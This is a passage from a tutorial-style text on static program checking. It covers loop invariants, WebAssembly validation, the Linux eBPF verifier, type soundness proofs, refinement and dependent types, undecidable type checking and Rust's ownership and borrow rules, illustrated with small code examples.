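2. Suppose the invariant is true and i < n. It must be true again after the two lines of the body. Working backwards, the rule for `s = s + i` requires s + i = 1 + … + i, and i ≤ n. The rule for `i = i + 1` turns this into s + (i + 1) = 1 + … + (i + 1), and i + 1 ≤ n. The first part follows from s = 1 + … + i. The second follows from i < n, since both are whole numbers.
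3. When the loop ends, the invariant is true and i < n is false. So i = n, and s = 1 + … + n.

The proof covers every n but requires checking the body only once. Between the two lines of the body the invariant is false, like the count in Dijkstra's room, because `i` has been updated and `s` has not. The rule permits this because it requires the invariant only at the start and end of a pass. If a `goto` elsewhere could land between the two lines, the proof would have to cover that entry too.

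Hoare lists jumps among the features that make proofs elaborate, but proofs about programs with jumps are still possible. Leroy (2021) traces program proofs to papers by Turing in 1949, Robert Floyd in 1967 and Hoare in *How can we reason about software?*. Floyd's method is for flowcharts, in which an arrow can lead anywhere. The prover must attach statements to enough points that every circular path passes through at least one of those points. In structured code without recursive procedures, the loops already mark them.

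The rules only check the invariant, so somebody still has to supply it. `i ≤ n` on its own also stays true after every pass, but it is too weak to prove anything about `s`. Tools can guess invariants for simple loops like this one, but, as with proof-carrying code, some correct programs have no proof.

The rules do not prove that a loop ends, either. Hoare's example divides x by y by subtracting y repeatedly, and he proves that on completion x equals the remainder plus y times the quotient. He allows y to be 0, in which case the program subtracts 0 forever. The theorem remains true because it covers only runs that finish. To prove termination, the checklist in *SE 504 Formal Methods and Models* requires a bound function, whose value is a whole number that is positive whenever the loop continues and decreases with each pass. For the sum, n − i is a bound function.

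The proof also assumes exact arithmetic. In a language whose largest integer is 2,147,483,647, a common limit, the sum overflows once n reaches 65,536. Hoare gives different axioms for different treatments of overflow, and a proof applies only to machines that satisfy the axiom it uses.

### The jumps that programmers keep

Dijkstra objected to the "unbridled use" of `goto` and left room for other constructs, such as one that abandons a computation, as long as the coordinates survive. Knuth (1974) examined particular cases in *Structured Programming with go to Statements*, arguing for removing some jumps and introducing others. One of his examples searches a table for an item, adds it if it is missing, and then increases its count. In C, it looks like this:

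```c
for (i = 0; i < m; i++)
    if (a[i] == x) goto found;
a[i] = x;
count[i] = 0;
m = m + 1;
found:
count[i] = count[i] + 1;
```

Without the jump, the program needs another test after the loop to determine why the loop ended. Knuth cared about the time such tests take in code that runs very often. The jump only leads forwards and out of the loop, so a reader can still tell that position `i` holds `x` at `found`.

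Most of the `goto` statements in modern C code seem to be of this tame kind. In *An Empirical Study of Goto in C Code from GitHub Repositories*, Nagappan and colleagues (2015) examined a representative sample of 384 files, drawn from almost 250,000 files in over 11,000 projects. About 80 per cent of the sampled files used `goto` to handle errors and about 40 per cent used it to release resources at the end of a function; some did both. The study also followed six projects after their releases, and in four of them developers did not remove or change a single `goto`.

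The study concludes that `goto` does not appear to be harmful in practice. That conclusion is reasonable for the jumps the study found, but it is weak evidence against Dijkstra's argument. The programmers were writing after decades of warnings about `goto`, and the study could not show how they would have managed with the tangled jumps he had in mind.

### WebAssembly: one pass over nested blocks

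WebAssembly is a low-level code format that web browsers and other programs can run. Compilers translate languages such as C into it, and the browser validates the code before running it. WebAssembly's branch instructions resemble the jumps that Knuth defended. A branch can leave an enclosing block or start the next pass of an enclosing loop, but it cannot jump into the middle of a block from outside.

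WebAssembly's *Validation Algorithm* reads the instructions once, in order. It keeps a value stack, which lists the types of the values that would be on the running program's stack, and a control stack, which has an entry for each open block. The following code counts local variable 0 down to zero. The comments show the value stack after each instruction, and `i32` means a 32-bit integer.

```
block
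  loop
    local.get 0    ;; i32
    i32.eqz        ;; i32 (is it zero?)
    br_if 1        ;; empty
    local.get 0    ;; i32
    i32.const 1    ;; i32 i32
    i32.sub        ;; i32
    local.set 0    ;; empty
    br 0           ;; empty
  end
end
```

The number after a branch counts outwards through the enclosing blocks. `br 0` refers to the loop, so it starts another pass, and `br_if 1` leaves the outer block if the test succeeded. For `i32.sub`, the validator removes two `i32` entries and adds one. If the code had `i64.const 1`, a 64-bit number, the types would not match and the validator would reject the module.

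One pass is enough because each block declares in advance which types it takes from the stack and which it leaves there. When the validator reaches a branch, it compares the value stack with the target block's declaration, which it has already read. For a loop, the declaration acts as an invariant, although it only states how many values of which types each iteration starts with. The compiler supplies this invariant, so the validator doesn't have to find it. W3C, which publishes web standards, justifies this design by noting that a browser can begin validating and compiling before the whole file has arrived.

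The specification calls the algorithm sound and complete, meaning that it accepts exactly the code that the validation rules allow. The validator can still raise false alarms about a program's behaviour. For example, it rejects a mismatched subtraction even in a branch that no run can reach.

The guarantee is also narrow. Deleting the first three instructions inside the loop makes the program run forever, but it still passes the check. The specification, WebAssembly (2024), warns that code from an unsafe language can corrupt its own data inside the memory block that WebAssembly gives it.

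### eBPF: every path, within a budget

The Linux kernel, the core of the operating system, applies a more ambitious check. eBPF lets users load small programs into the running kernel, for example to filter network traffic. As *The eBPF Runtime in the Linux Kernel* (2024) describes, each program must first pass a verifier. A bad memory access or an endless loop in the kernel could bring down the whole machine. In the comments on LWN's *A different approach to BPF loops* (2021), one reader asks why the kernel does not simply count instructions while a program runs. Another replies that compiled code runs faster but needs verification first.

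The verifier follows the possible paths through the program and simulates each instruction. According to the Linux kernel documentation's *eBPF verifier*, it tracks whether the program has written to each register (a storage slot in the processor), whether the register holds an address or a number, and what range the number can have. After a test for "greater than 8", for instance, it sets the minimum to 9 on one branch and the maximum to 8 on the other. In one example, a program reads the 13th and 14th bytes of a network packet. The program first tests whether the packet has at least 14 bytes, and the verifier accepts the read on the branch where it does. Without the test, the verifier would reject the program, even if every packet that arrived were long enough.

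The number of paths can grow very fast. Twenty `if` statements in a row give 2²⁰ paths, just over a million. So at each branch the verifier looks for a state it has already accepted at the same instruction. If that state covers every case in the current one, the verifier does not need to explore the path again.

The Linux kernel documentation's *BPF Design Q&A* lists the limits. The verifier simulates at most 1 million instructions, counting repeats, and rejects any program that needs more. A program may use 512 bytes of stack memory. A user without special privileges may load programs of at most 4,096 instructions. There are also limits on branches, nested calls and stored states. According to the documentation, the only way to find out whether the verifier will accept a program is to try to load it.

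Programmers notice this unpredictability. The verifier reads compiled code, which has lost some of the information in the source. According to *Prevail: Understanding the Windows eBPF Verifier* (2023), small changes to a large program or to the compiler's options can lead to a rejection. Chaignon reports in *Fix invariant violation for single-value tnums* that a bug in the verifier sometimes made it reject programs belonging to Cilium, a widely used networking system, and prevented Cilium from starting. Another bug, in the handling of `bpf_loop`, made the verifier accept an unsafe program until Zingerman fixed it.

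Loops are the hardest part. The verifier at first rejected them all, but since Linux 5.3 in 2019 it has accepted loops with a fixed bound. *SCEV-based Loop Analysis for the BPF Verifier* (Zingerman, 2026), a talk to kernel developers, explained that the verifier simulated such loops one pass at a time. If a loop of 1,000 passes contains another loop of 1,000 passes with ten instructions, the simulation takes 10 million steps, which exceeds the budget even if the program is safe.

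Zingerman's remedy has the verifier infer a simple invariant itself. If `i` starts at 0 and grows by 1 while it is below 1,000, then `i` is between 0 and 999 at the start of every pass. The verifier can check the body once for that whole range, and it has no new cases to check when it returns to the top of the loop. This works only for variables that change by a constant amount. If another variable changes less regularly, the wide range for `i` can make the verifier check an exit after every pass, so it has 1,000 exits to explore instead of one.

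He tried a prototype on 6,705 programs, 382 of which had needed more than 10,000 simulated instructions. For 89 of those 382, the number of simulated instructions fell by more than half. But 38 programs that had previously passed now failed, five of them because they reached the limit of 1 million. Each of those failures would break the kernel developers' promise that later versions will accept every program that earlier ones accepted. The developers have since begun to merge this kind of analysis into the branch where they prepare future releases.

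A proposal from November 2025, *bpf: Introduce proof-based verifier enhancement*, instead has the program's supplier provide proofs, much as proof-carrying code does. When the verifier reaches a path that looks unsafe, it sends out the conditions for taking that path. A theorem prover outside the kernel then tries to show that these conditions contradict each other. In one example, the prover returned a 715-step proof of about 17 kilobytes. The kernel checked each step, confirming that no run could take the path, and accepted the program.

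## Write typing rules and prove them sound

WebAssembly's validator follows rules about the types of values that each instruction takes from the stack and leaves on it. Type checkers for ordinary programming languages follow similar rules for expressions. A very small language is enough to show how to write such rules and prove that they guarantee something about a program's behaviour.

### A small language

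A program in this language is a single expression, which can take any of these forms:

```
0  1  2  ...               a number
true  false                a boolean
x                          a variable
e1 + e2                    a sum
if e1 then e2 else e3      a conditional
fun (x : T) => e           a function with parameter x of type T
e1 e2                      the function e1 applied to e2
```

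The types are `int`, `bool` and S → T, which is the type of functions that take an S and return a T. Numbers, booleans and functions are values, meaning finished results. To run a program, the machine rewrites it one step at a time until it reaches a value. With ↦ for "steps to", the basic steps are:

- `2 + 3` ↦ `5`, and likewise for any other two numbers.
- `if true then e2 else e3` ↦ `e2`, and `if false then e2 else e3` ↦ `e3`.
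- `(fun (x : T) => e) v` ↦ `e` with the value `v` in place of `x`.

If no basic step applies to the whole expression, the machine takes a step inside it, working from left to right. In a conditional, it evaluates only the condition until it can choose a branch.

Some expressions, such as `1 + true`, are not values but have no next step. *Types*, a chapter of the online textbook *Software Foundations*, calls them stuck and gives `if 42 then 0 else 1` as another example. In a real implementation, getting stuck corresponds to executing an illegal instruction. The goal is to guarantee that a program never gets stuck.

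No checker can decide this property exactly. If we ignore the types, these few forms can express every computable function, so the argument about closed files applies again. A program could run an arbitrary computation and then evaluate `1 + true`.

### The rules

The notation Γ ⊢ e : T means that the expression e has type T if its variables have the types listed in Γ. For a complete program, Γ is empty.

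| Rule | To conclude | First show | In words |
|---|---|---|---|
| Num | Γ ⊢ n : int | nothing | Every number is an `int`. |
| Bool | Γ ⊢ true : bool, Γ ⊢ false : bool | nothing | `true` and `false` are booleans. |
| Var | Γ ⊢ x : T | Γ contains x : T | A variable has the type that Γ lists for it. |
| Add | Γ ⊢ e1 + e2 : int | Γ ⊢ e1 : int, Γ ⊢ e2 : int | Both parts of a sum must be numbers, and so is the result. |
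| If | Γ ⊢ if e1 then e2 else e3 : T | Γ ⊢ e1 : bool, Γ ⊢ e2 : T, Γ ⊢ e3 : T | The condition must be a boolean, and both branches must have the same type. |
| Fun | Γ ⊢ fun (x : S) => e : S → T | Γ, x : S ⊢ e : T | If the body has type T when x has type S, the function takes an S and returns a T. |
| App | Γ ⊢ e1 e2 : T | Γ ⊢ e1 : S → T, Γ ⊢ e2 : S | The argument must have the type that the function takes. |

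A program is well-typed if there is a derivation for it, which is a list of conclusions that each follow from earlier ones by a rule. Here is a derivation for a program that applies a function to `true`:

```
1  b : bool ⊢ b : bool                                    Var
2  b : bool ⊢ 1 : int                                     Num
3  b : bool ⊢ 2 : int                                     Num
4  b : bool ⊢ if b then 1 else 2 : int                    If, from 1, 2, 3
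5  ⊢ fun (b : bool) => if b then 1 else 2 : bool → int    Fun, from 4
6  ⊢ true : bool                                          Bool
7  ⊢ (fun (b : bool) => if b then 1 else 2) true : int    App, from 5, 6
```

When the program runs, it steps to `if true then 1 else 2` and then to `1`, which is an `int`, as predicted in the last line.

If the argument is `5` instead of `true`, the program has no derivation. App requires an argument of type `bool`, but the only rule for `5` gives it type `int`. Rejecting the program is correct, because it would step to `if 5 then 1 else 2` and get stuck.

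Rejecting the program `if true then 1 else 1 + true` is a false alarm. The program steps to `1` without evaluating the bad sum, but the rule If needs a type for both branches, and `1 + true` has none. A designer could add a rule that ignores the `else` branch when the condition is the word `true`. *Types* sets this idea as a quiz question. The extra rule is harmless but gains little, since it does not help with a condition such as `if true then true else false`.

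Milner (1978), in *A Theory of Type Polymorphism in Programming*, gives an example of a false alarm that a programmer might meet. A function `F` takes another function and a pair of values, and applies the function to both values. Using `F` to reverse a list of numbers and a list of words would be harmless, but Milner's system rejects this use because both values must have the same type. He was unsure how much of a burden such rejections would be.

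### Progress and preservation

Milner was also the first to state and prove a type soundness theorem, with the slogan that well-typed programs cannot "go wrong". He gave each program a mathematical meaning, with a special meaning, "wrong", for type errors, and proved that no well-typed program has it. According to Timany, Krebbers and colleagues (2024), in *A Logical Approach to Type Soundness*, this method was hard to extend to languages with features such as updatable memory and concurrency. Wright and Felleisen (1994), in *A Syntactic Approach to Type Soundness*, reasoned about the steps of a run instead, and their method extended easily to updatable memory and exceptions. Robert Harper later suggested organising the proof around two theorems:

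- Preservation: if ⊢ e : T and e ↦ e′, then ⊢ e′ : T.
- Progress: if ⊢ e : T, then e is a value or there is some e′ with e ↦ e′.

We prove each theorem one rule at a time, assuming in each case that the theorem already holds for the smaller expressions inside the one we are considering. For conditionals, suppose that `if e1 then e2 else e3` has type T. Only the rule If gives a type to a conditional, so e1 has type `bool`, and e2 and e3 both have type T.

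For progress, we may assume that e1 is a value or can take a step.

1. If e1 can step to some e1′, the whole expression steps to `if e1′ then e2 else e3`.
2. If e1 is a value, it must be `true` or `false`, because numbers have type `int` and functions have types of the form S → T. The whole expression then steps to e2 or e3.

For preservation, suppose that the conditional takes a step. There are three possibilities.

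1. It steps to e2, which has type T.
2. It steps to e3, which also has type T.
3. It steps to `if e1′ then e2 else e3` because e1 ↦ e1′. We may assume preservation for e1, so e1′ has type `bool`, and the rule If gives the new conditional type T.

A mistake in a typing rule makes some case of the soundness proof impossible to prove. If the `If` rule did not require the condition e1 to be a boolean, the proof of progress would fail when e1 is a value, since e1 might be `5`. If the rule took the expression's type from e2 and ignored e3, the proof of preservation would fail when the expression steps to e3.

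The function application case of the proof also needs the substitution lemma. If a function body has type T when x has type S, it still has type T after a value of type S replaces x. *StlcProp*, a later chapter of *Software Foundations*, gives this part of the proof.

Type soundness follows from the two theorems together. Suppose a well-typed program has taken any number of steps. By preservation, every step leaves the expression well-typed, so the current expression is well-typed. By progress, it is a value or can take another step, so it is not stuck. Milner pointed out the practical benefit that compiled code does not have to carry types or check them at run time.

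Every new language feature needs its own cases in the proof, and features can interact. ML, the language for which Milner designed his system, allows a function such as list reversal to work on lists of any element type. It also has reference cells, which are memory locations that a program can overwrite. Consider this program in outline:

```
r = a new cell that holds the empty list
store the list [1] in r
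if (the first element of the list in r) then 2 else 3
```

The empty list is a list of numbers and also a list of booleans. If the checker lets `r` hold lists of any type, it can treat `r` as a cell for numbers on the second line and for booleans on the third. The program then gets stuck at `if 1`. To prevent this, `r` must keep a single type if its definition creates a cell. *Weak polymorphism can be sound* notes that no algorithm can decide in every case whether an expression creates one. Mads Tofte's rule therefore assumes that any expression not already written as a value may create a cell, which the checker can test from the text.

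### What the theorem leaves open

A sound type system does not prevent wrong answers. `fun (x : int) => x + 1` has type int → int even if the programmer meant to add 2.

Type soundness also doesn't guarantee that a program stops. Tatlock's lecture slides *Type Safety* (2016) state the theorem that a well-typed program either reaches a value or runs forever. In the small language, every well-typed program stops because the rules reject functions that apply themselves. For `x x` to have a type, x would need a type S equal to S → T, and no finite type satisfies that equation. But practical languages let functions call themselves by name, so their well-typed programs can loop forever.

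The theorem also allows any error that the designer has chosen to permit. *Type Safety*, a chapter of Harper's textbook, considers adding a division operator to a language. `3 / 0` is well-typed because both operands are numbers, but it is stuck. The designer can make the typing rules stricter, so that they accept only divisors the checker can show to be non-zero, or add a run-time check that ends the program with an error. Most designers choose the run-time check, because stricter rules would reject too many good programs. Progress then means that a well-typed expression is a value, can take a step, or is one of the permitted errors.

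A claim of type soundness therefore means little without the list of permitted errors, which usually includes reading past the end of an array. A designer could add `1 + true` and every other stuck expression to the list, and the theorem would hold for all programs without any typing rules. *Safety and Soundness*, a chapter of a Brown University textbook, emphasises the guarantee that no error outside the list can happen.

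### Abstract types

Programmers can make types guarantee more. The cheapest way is to hide how a program constructs the values of a type. In this OCaml module (OCaml is a descendant of ML), the part after `sig` is public and the part after `struct` is private:

```ocaml
module Address : sig
  type t
  val validate : string -> t option
  val to_string : t -> string
end = struct
  type t = string
  let validate s =
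    if String.contains s '@' then Some s else None
  let to_string a = a
end
```

The module represents an address as a `string`, but outside the module `Address.t` and `string` are different types, and only `validate` produces an `Address.t`. If a function `send` takes an `Address.t`, the checker rejects `send "nobody"`. Every address that reaches `send` has therefore passed the check in `validate`, so `send` doesn't need to repeat it.

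The programmer has to write the interface and the validator, and handle a `None` result wherever text enters the program. A module could protect files in the same way, by offering one function that opens a file, reads it, closes it and returns the text. Code outside the module would never hold the file, so it could not try to read it after it was closed.

The type checker does not check whether the validator is correct, and the validator above accepts `@@@`. Anyone who edits the module can add a second function that returns unchecked text as an `Address.t`. A valid address can also stop working after the check.

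Progress and preservation do not even show that a module's private data is protected from other code. Timany and colleagues give a language an operation called `gremlin` that may set any whole number in memory to 0. Both theorems still hold because the operation replaces one whole number with another, but a module can no longer rely on its private counter only increasing. Java's reflection feature similarly let any code change an object's private data until version 9 gave programmers a way to prevent this. Timany and colleagues therefore recommend proving a stronger theorem, in which a type is defined by how its values behave. This theorem can also cover a module that uses unchecked casts internally.

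### Refinement types

A refinement type adds a condition to an ordinary type. Jhala and Vazou (2020), in *Refinement Types*, use such types to prevent reads outside an array. In a simplified notation, the two basic array operations have these types:

```
size : (x : array) → {n : int | n = length(x) and 0 ≤ n}
get  : (x : array) → {i : int | 0 ≤ i and i < length(x)} → int
```

So `size` returns the length of the array, and `get` accepts only positions inside it. Positions start at 0. Suppose a programmer writes a function that returns the last element:

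```
last x = get x (size x - 1)
```

Let n be the result of `size x`, and i the position that `last` passes to `get`. The checker turns the call into a condition that must be true for all arrays and numbers:

> If 0 ≤ length(x), n = length(x) and i = n − 1, then 0 ≤ i and i < length(x).

The checker sends this to an SMT (satisfiability modulo theories) solver, a program that decides whether a set of logical and arithmetical conditions has a solution. As *Partial Automation of Verification Condition Proving for Reflex Programs (Draft)* (2026) explains, the solver looks for a violation, which here means values that satisfy everything before "then" but make i negative or greater than or equal to length(x). It finds length(x) = 0, n = 0 and i = −1, so the checker rejects the program. The error is real, since an empty array has no last element.

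The programmer can add a test:

```
last x = if 0 < size x then get x (size x - 1) else 0
```

The checker adds 0 < n to the conditions for the first branch. Now i = n − 1 is at least 0, because n is a whole number greater than 0, and i is less than length(x), because n equals length(x). The solver reports that no violation exists, and the checker accepts the program. *Refinement Types for TypeScript* (2016) uses the same method for a function that returns the first element of an array. The programmer could also leave out the test and declare that `last` takes only non-empty arrays. Every call to `last` would then have to meet that condition.

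The programmer mainly writes conditions on the inputs and outputs of functions, and tools can infer many of the conditions in between. Missing conditions cause false alarms. Suppose a function `copy` has the type array → array. If a program checks that `x` is non-empty and then reads position 0 of `copy x`, the checker rejects the program because the type of `copy` does not relate the length of the output to the length of the input. Adding the condition that the lengths are equal fixes this if the checker can confirm it from the body of `copy`.

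Jhala and Vazou restrict the conditions to a logic that solvers can always decide. This logic includes addition and comparison of whole numbers but not, for example, statements about all numbers. Some verification tools, such as Dafny and F*, allow such statements, but their solvers then rely on heuristics, so whether a program passes can depend on the solver.

The guarantee also holds only if the basic operations have correct types. Like Hoare's proofs, Jhala and Vazou's examples assume exact arithmetic, so overflow can break the guarantee. A designer can give addition a stricter type that rules out overflow, but programmers must then satisfy more conditions.

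### Dependent types

In a dependent type system, types can contain arbitrary expressions of the language, and the programmer can write proofs as part of the program. A proposition is a type, and a proof of it is a program of that type. The rule App already has the right form for this. If one reads S → T as "S implies T", the rule states that a proof of "S implies T" and a proof of S together give a proof of T. A proof of "A and B" is a pair, so this function proves that "A and B" implies "B and A":

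```
fun (p : A and B) => (second p, first p)
```

The checker can verify the proof just by checking the function's type. In such a language, `get` can require the caller to supply a third argument, a proof that the position is inside the array.

*PLFA agda exercises* writes the progress theorem as a function in Agda, a dependently typed language. The function takes a typing derivation and returns evidence that the expression is a value or can take a step. For conditionals, it first checks whether the condition can step and, if not, whether it is true or false, as in the proof above.

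A drawback is that programmers must often prove facts that seem obvious. Let `Vec n` be the type of lists with exactly n elements. Appending a `Vec m` and a `Vec n` gives a `Vec (m + n)`, so appending an empty list to a `Vec n` gives a `Vec (n + 0)`. Agda's usual definition of addition proceeds by cases on the first number, so the checker can simplify 0 + n to n but can't simplify n + 0. If the program needs a `Vec n`, the checker rejects the result until the programmer supplies a proof that n + 0 = n.

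Proofs of this kind prove nothing if programs can loop forever. A function defined by `f n = f n` never returns, so a checker could give it any result type, including one that stands for a false proposition. Proof languages therefore require programs to be total, as Turner's languages do, and reject some functions that do stop.

The proof may also establish the wrong property. If a sorting function's type requires only that the output be a list in ascending order, a function that always returns the empty list satisfies it. The type must also require the output to contain the same elements as the input.

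### When type checking is undecidable

If the types of a language can express arbitrary computations, type checking itself becomes undecidable. It might seem enough to say that the checker would have to run those computations and some never stop. But as *Why does a Turing-complete type system make type checking undecidable?* (2017) points out, a checker might not need to run them all. The post instead puts a halting question into a type annotation, in a construction it credits to Kamal Marhubi. Here is a version of it:

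```python
n: int_after(p, x) = 1
```

`int_after(p, x)` is a computation in the language of types. It runs the program `p` on the input `x` and, if `p` stops, returns the type `int`. If `p` stops on `x`, the annotation amounts to `int`, and the line is well-typed because 1 is an `int`. If `p` runs forever, the annotation never produces a type, so the line is not well-typed. A checker that always gave the right answer would therefore solve the halting problem. (In the post, the annotation is one type if the program stops and another if it does not. No computation could choose between them, but the argument only requires running the program.)

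Some widely used languages have this problem, although their designers never set out to put a programming language into the types. Grigore (2016), in *Java Generics are Turing Complete*, showed how to turn any Turing machine, a simple mathematical model of a computer, into a set of Java classes and a question about whether one type is a subtype of another. The answer is yes exactly when the machine halts. Roth (2022), in *Python Type Hints are Turing Complete*, applied the method to Python's annotations. He also gives a short program that makes the checking go on forever. With different names, it looks like this:

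```python
import typing as t

A = t.TypeVar("A", contravariant=True)
B = t.TypeVar("B")

class Sink(t.Generic[A]):
    pass

class Grow(t.Generic[B], Sink[Sink["Grow[Grow[B]]"]]):
    pass

item: Sink[Grow[t.Any]] = Grow[t.Any]()
```

The last line is well-typed only if `Grow[Any]` is a subtype of `Sink[Grow[Any]]`. The word `contravariant` means that `Sink[S]` is a subtype of `Sink[T]` if T is a subtype of S, so the direction reverses. (In the same way, a function that accepts any object can stand in for one that accepts only numbers.) The definition of `Grow` makes `Grow[Any]` a subtype of `Sink[Sink[Grow[Grow[Any]]]]`. To compare that with `Sink[Grow[Any]]`, the checker removes the outer `Sink` from both and reverses the direction, which leaves another question of the same form. With `<:` for "is a subtype of", the questions continue like this:

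```
Grow[Any]        <:  Sink[Grow[Any]]
Grow[Any]        <:  Sink[Grow[Grow[Any]]]
Grow[Grow[Any]]  <:  Sink[Grow[Grow[Any]]]
Grow[Grow[Any]]  <:  Sink[Grow[Grow[Grow[Any]]]]
```

The types keep growing, and the first question never gets an answer. Mypy crashed when Roth ran it on this program, apparently because it ran out of memory for nested calls.

A language designer can forbid the pattern that causes the growth, in which a class inherits from ever larger types built from itself. Andrew Kennedy and Benjamin Pierce proved in 2007 that this restriction makes the subtype question decidable in the simplified system they studied. Scala and Microsoft's .NET have such restrictions, although Grigore notes that type checking in Scala is still undecidable for other reasons. Adding one to Python would make some currently valid programs invalid.

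Compilers can also set a limit on depth. The Rust compiler reports an error when certain compile-time computations nest too deeply, and programmers can raise the limit with the `recursion_limit` setting. The C++ compiler GCC has a similar option, `-ftemplate-depth`. A sound checker with such a limit stays sound as long as it rejects every program that reaches the limit. But the limit adds false alarms, and a program may pass with one setting and fail with another. Few programmers write such classes by accident, but Grigore notes that somebody could use them to attack a compiler, so a service that checks strangers' code needs to limit time and memory as well.

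## Track ownership and borrowing

The typing rules in the previous section give a variable the same type for as long as it exists, so mypy accepts a program that reads a file after closing it. The same problem has worse consequences with memory, where one part of a program can free or rearrange data that another part is still using. Rust, a language for operating systems, browsers and other software that needs close control of memory, adds rules about which parts of a program may refer to a value and which may change it.

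### Errors that ordinary types miss

This C++ program keeps three numbers in a vector, which is a list that can grow:

```cpp
std::vector<int> v = {10, 20, 30};
int& first = v[0];
v.push_back(40);
std::cout << first;
```

`first` is a reference, which here means that it holds the address of the vector's first element. A vector stores its elements side by side in one block of memory. If the block is full, `push_back` obtains a larger block, copies the elements into it and frees the old one. `first` still holds the old address, so the last line may read memory that has already been freed, an error called use-after-free. The types are correct on every line, since `first` is a reference to an `int` throughout.

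Iterator invalidation is a similar error in a loop. This Python program removes an element from the list it is going through:

```python
xs = [1, 2, 3, 4]
for x in xs:
    print(x)
    if x == 2:
        xs.remove(x)
```

A Python loop that prints each number in the list [1, 2, 3, 4] and removes the 2 after printing it prints only 1, 2 and 4. The loop tracks its position in the list, and removing the 2 shifts the 3 into a position the loop has already visited. In C++, adding elements to a vector while looping over it can make the loop read freed memory.

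A data race occurs when two threads, parts of a program that run at the same time, use the same memory without coordination and at least one writes to it. Suppose a counter holds 5 and two threads each add 1. Both may read 5 and then write 6, so one addition is lost.

All three errors require a second way to reach some data, called an alias, and a change to the data while the alias is still in use. Either is harmless without the other, so Rust permits aliases or changes at any moment, but not both. *Verified Implementation of the Next-gen Borrow Checking Algorithm for Rust* (Wu, Wang and Chen, 2026) calls this rule "Aliasing XOR Mutability", where XOR means "one or the other but not both".

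### From linear logic to Rust

Weiss, Gierczak and colleagues (2019) trace Rust's idea of ownership back to linear logic, which Jean-Yves Girard introduced in 1987. A proof in linear logic must use each assumption exactly once, whereas ordinary logic allows any number of uses. Using an assumption in linear logic consumes it, just as someone who spends a coin on a coffee no longer has the coin.

Linear types treat variables this way. The rule App in the previous section checks a function and its argument with the same list of variables Γ, so both can use every variable. The linear version divides the list into two parts with no variable in common:

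> If Γ₁ ⊢ e1 : S → T and Γ₂ ⊢ e2 : S, then Γ₁, Γ₂ ⊢ e1 e2 : T.

The rule Var also changes, and now applies to x only if x is the only variable in the list. With both changes, a well-typed program uses each variable exactly once. An affine type system relaxes this to "at most once", so a program may leave a variable unused but may not use it twice.

Around 1990, Philip Wadler and Henry Baker designed systems of this kind for languages without a garbage collector, the run-time component that finds and frees unused memory. If a value has only one reference, the program can free or overwrite the value as soon as it has used that reference. Weiss and colleagues recall the objection that Wadler's approach depended on copying a lot of data. They consider Rust closer to Baker's approach, which reused objects in memory.

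In the 1990s, Mads Tofte and Jean-Pierre Talpin developed a system in which a program places values in regions of memory and frees each region all at once. A pointer's type includes the name of its region, so a checker can reject any use of the pointer after the region is freed. Cyclone, a safer dialect of C, added region names to C's pointer types in the early 2000s.

Rust draws on both lines of work. Ownership determines when a program frees a value. The type of each reference includes a lifetime, a name that limits how long the reference may last.

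### Moves and borrows

Every value in Rust has one owner, usually a variable. When the owner goes out of scope, typically at the end of the block that declares it, the program frees the value. Code can use a variable `a` in three ways:

| Operation | Example | What it permits | What it forbids |
|---|---|---|---|
| Move | `let b = a;` | `b` becomes the owner | Any later use of `a`, unless the program first gives it a new value |
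| Shared borrow | `let r = &a;` | Reading through `r`, and any number of other shared borrows | Changing or moving `a` while `r` is in use |
| Exclusive borrow | `let r = &mut a;` | Reading and changing the value through `r` | Any other use of `a` while `r` is in use |

Passing a value to a function also moves it. Numbers and other simple values are an exception, because Rust copies them instead.

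These rules prevent data races. A thread can change data only if it owns the data or has an exclusive reference to it, and while it does, no other thread can access that data. If several threads need to change the same counter, the programmer can put the counter in a `Mutex`, a lock that only one thread can hold at a time. Each thread has a shared reference to the lock, which enforces exclusive access while the program runs.

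Weiss and colleagues give examples of how finely the rules distinguish cases. If `p` is a pair of numbers, two exclusive references to `p` conflict, but an exclusive reference to `p.0` and another to `p.1` do not, because the parts do not overlap. A program can also create an exclusive reference `y` from another one, `x`, but it cannot use `x` again until it has finished with `y`. Several exclusive references to the same data can therefore exist together, as long as the program finishes with the newest one first.

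### Making `close` consume the file

Chen, Long and Xie (2026), in *A Calculus for Borrowability*, use files to show what linear types can guarantee and why programmers also want borrowing. In a purely linear language, `close` takes a file and returns nothing. A program that closes `f` and then reads it would use `f` twice, so the checker rejects it. The checker also rejects a program that opens a file and never closes it. But every other operation uses up the file too, and has to return it for the next one. Two writes and a close look like this:

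```
let f1 = write f "started" in
let f2 = write f1 "done" in
close f2
```

A program cannot pass `f` twice to a function that only wants to read it, either. Borrowing removes both inconveniences. Here is a simplified interface in Rust:

```rust
fn open(path: &str) -> File
fn read(f: &File) -> String
fn close(f: File)
```

`read` borrows the file, and only `close` takes it away from its owner. The program that reads a file after closing it now fails the check:

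```rust
let f = open("notes.txt");
close(f);
let text = read(&f);    // error: f has moved
```

The same rule rejects the earlier program that closes its file inside a loop, because the second pass would use a file that was moved during the first. The rule still applies if the program gives the file a second name. After `let g = f;`, the file belongs to `g`, and the program can no longer use `f`. Unlike the line-order rule from the first section, an ownership checker follows the file along every path through the program.

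It still raises a false alarm about the earlier program that tests the length of its path, because one branch moves the file before the `read`.

Rust's standard library has no `close` function for files. It closes a file when the file's owner goes out of scope, so a programmer cannot forget to close it, but the program does not find out if closing fails.

Robert Strom and Shaula Yemini gave the general idea the name "typestate" in 1986. A type determines which operations a value supports at all, and a typestate determines which of them it supports at a particular point in the program. In Rust, a programmer can give each state its own type:

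```rust
fn read(f: &OpenFile) -> String
fn close(f: OpenFile) -> ClosedFile
fn reopen(f: ClosedFile) -> Result<OpenFile, ClosedFile>
```

`read` accepts only an open file. `close` consumes the open file and returns a closed one. The program can later pass the closed file to `reopen`, which returns an open file if it succeeds and a closed one if it fails, so the program must test which it received before reading. Without ownership, separate types would not stop a program from reading a closed file. In Python, for example, a program could call `close(f)` and then pass `f`, whose type is still `OpenFile`, to `read`.

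### The borrow checker by hand

Moves are the simpler part of the check. For borrows, the compiler has to work out which references the program may still use at each point and which data they depend on. Here is the vector program in Rust, with numbered lines:

```rust
let mut v = vec![10, 20, 30];   // 1
let first = &v[0];              // 2
v.push(40);                     // 3
println!("{}", first);          // 4
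```

The checker's record of a borrow is called a loan. It consists of the data that the program has borrowed and whether the borrow is shared or exclusive. The rules that Wu and colleagues set out lead to an error in four steps:

1. Draw the control-flow graph, which has an arrow from each line to every line that can run next. Here the arrows are 1 → 2 → 3 → 4.
2. Find the live references, those that the program may still use. Line 4 uses `first`. Working backwards from there, `first` is live at the start of lines 4 and 3, but not before line 2 creates it.
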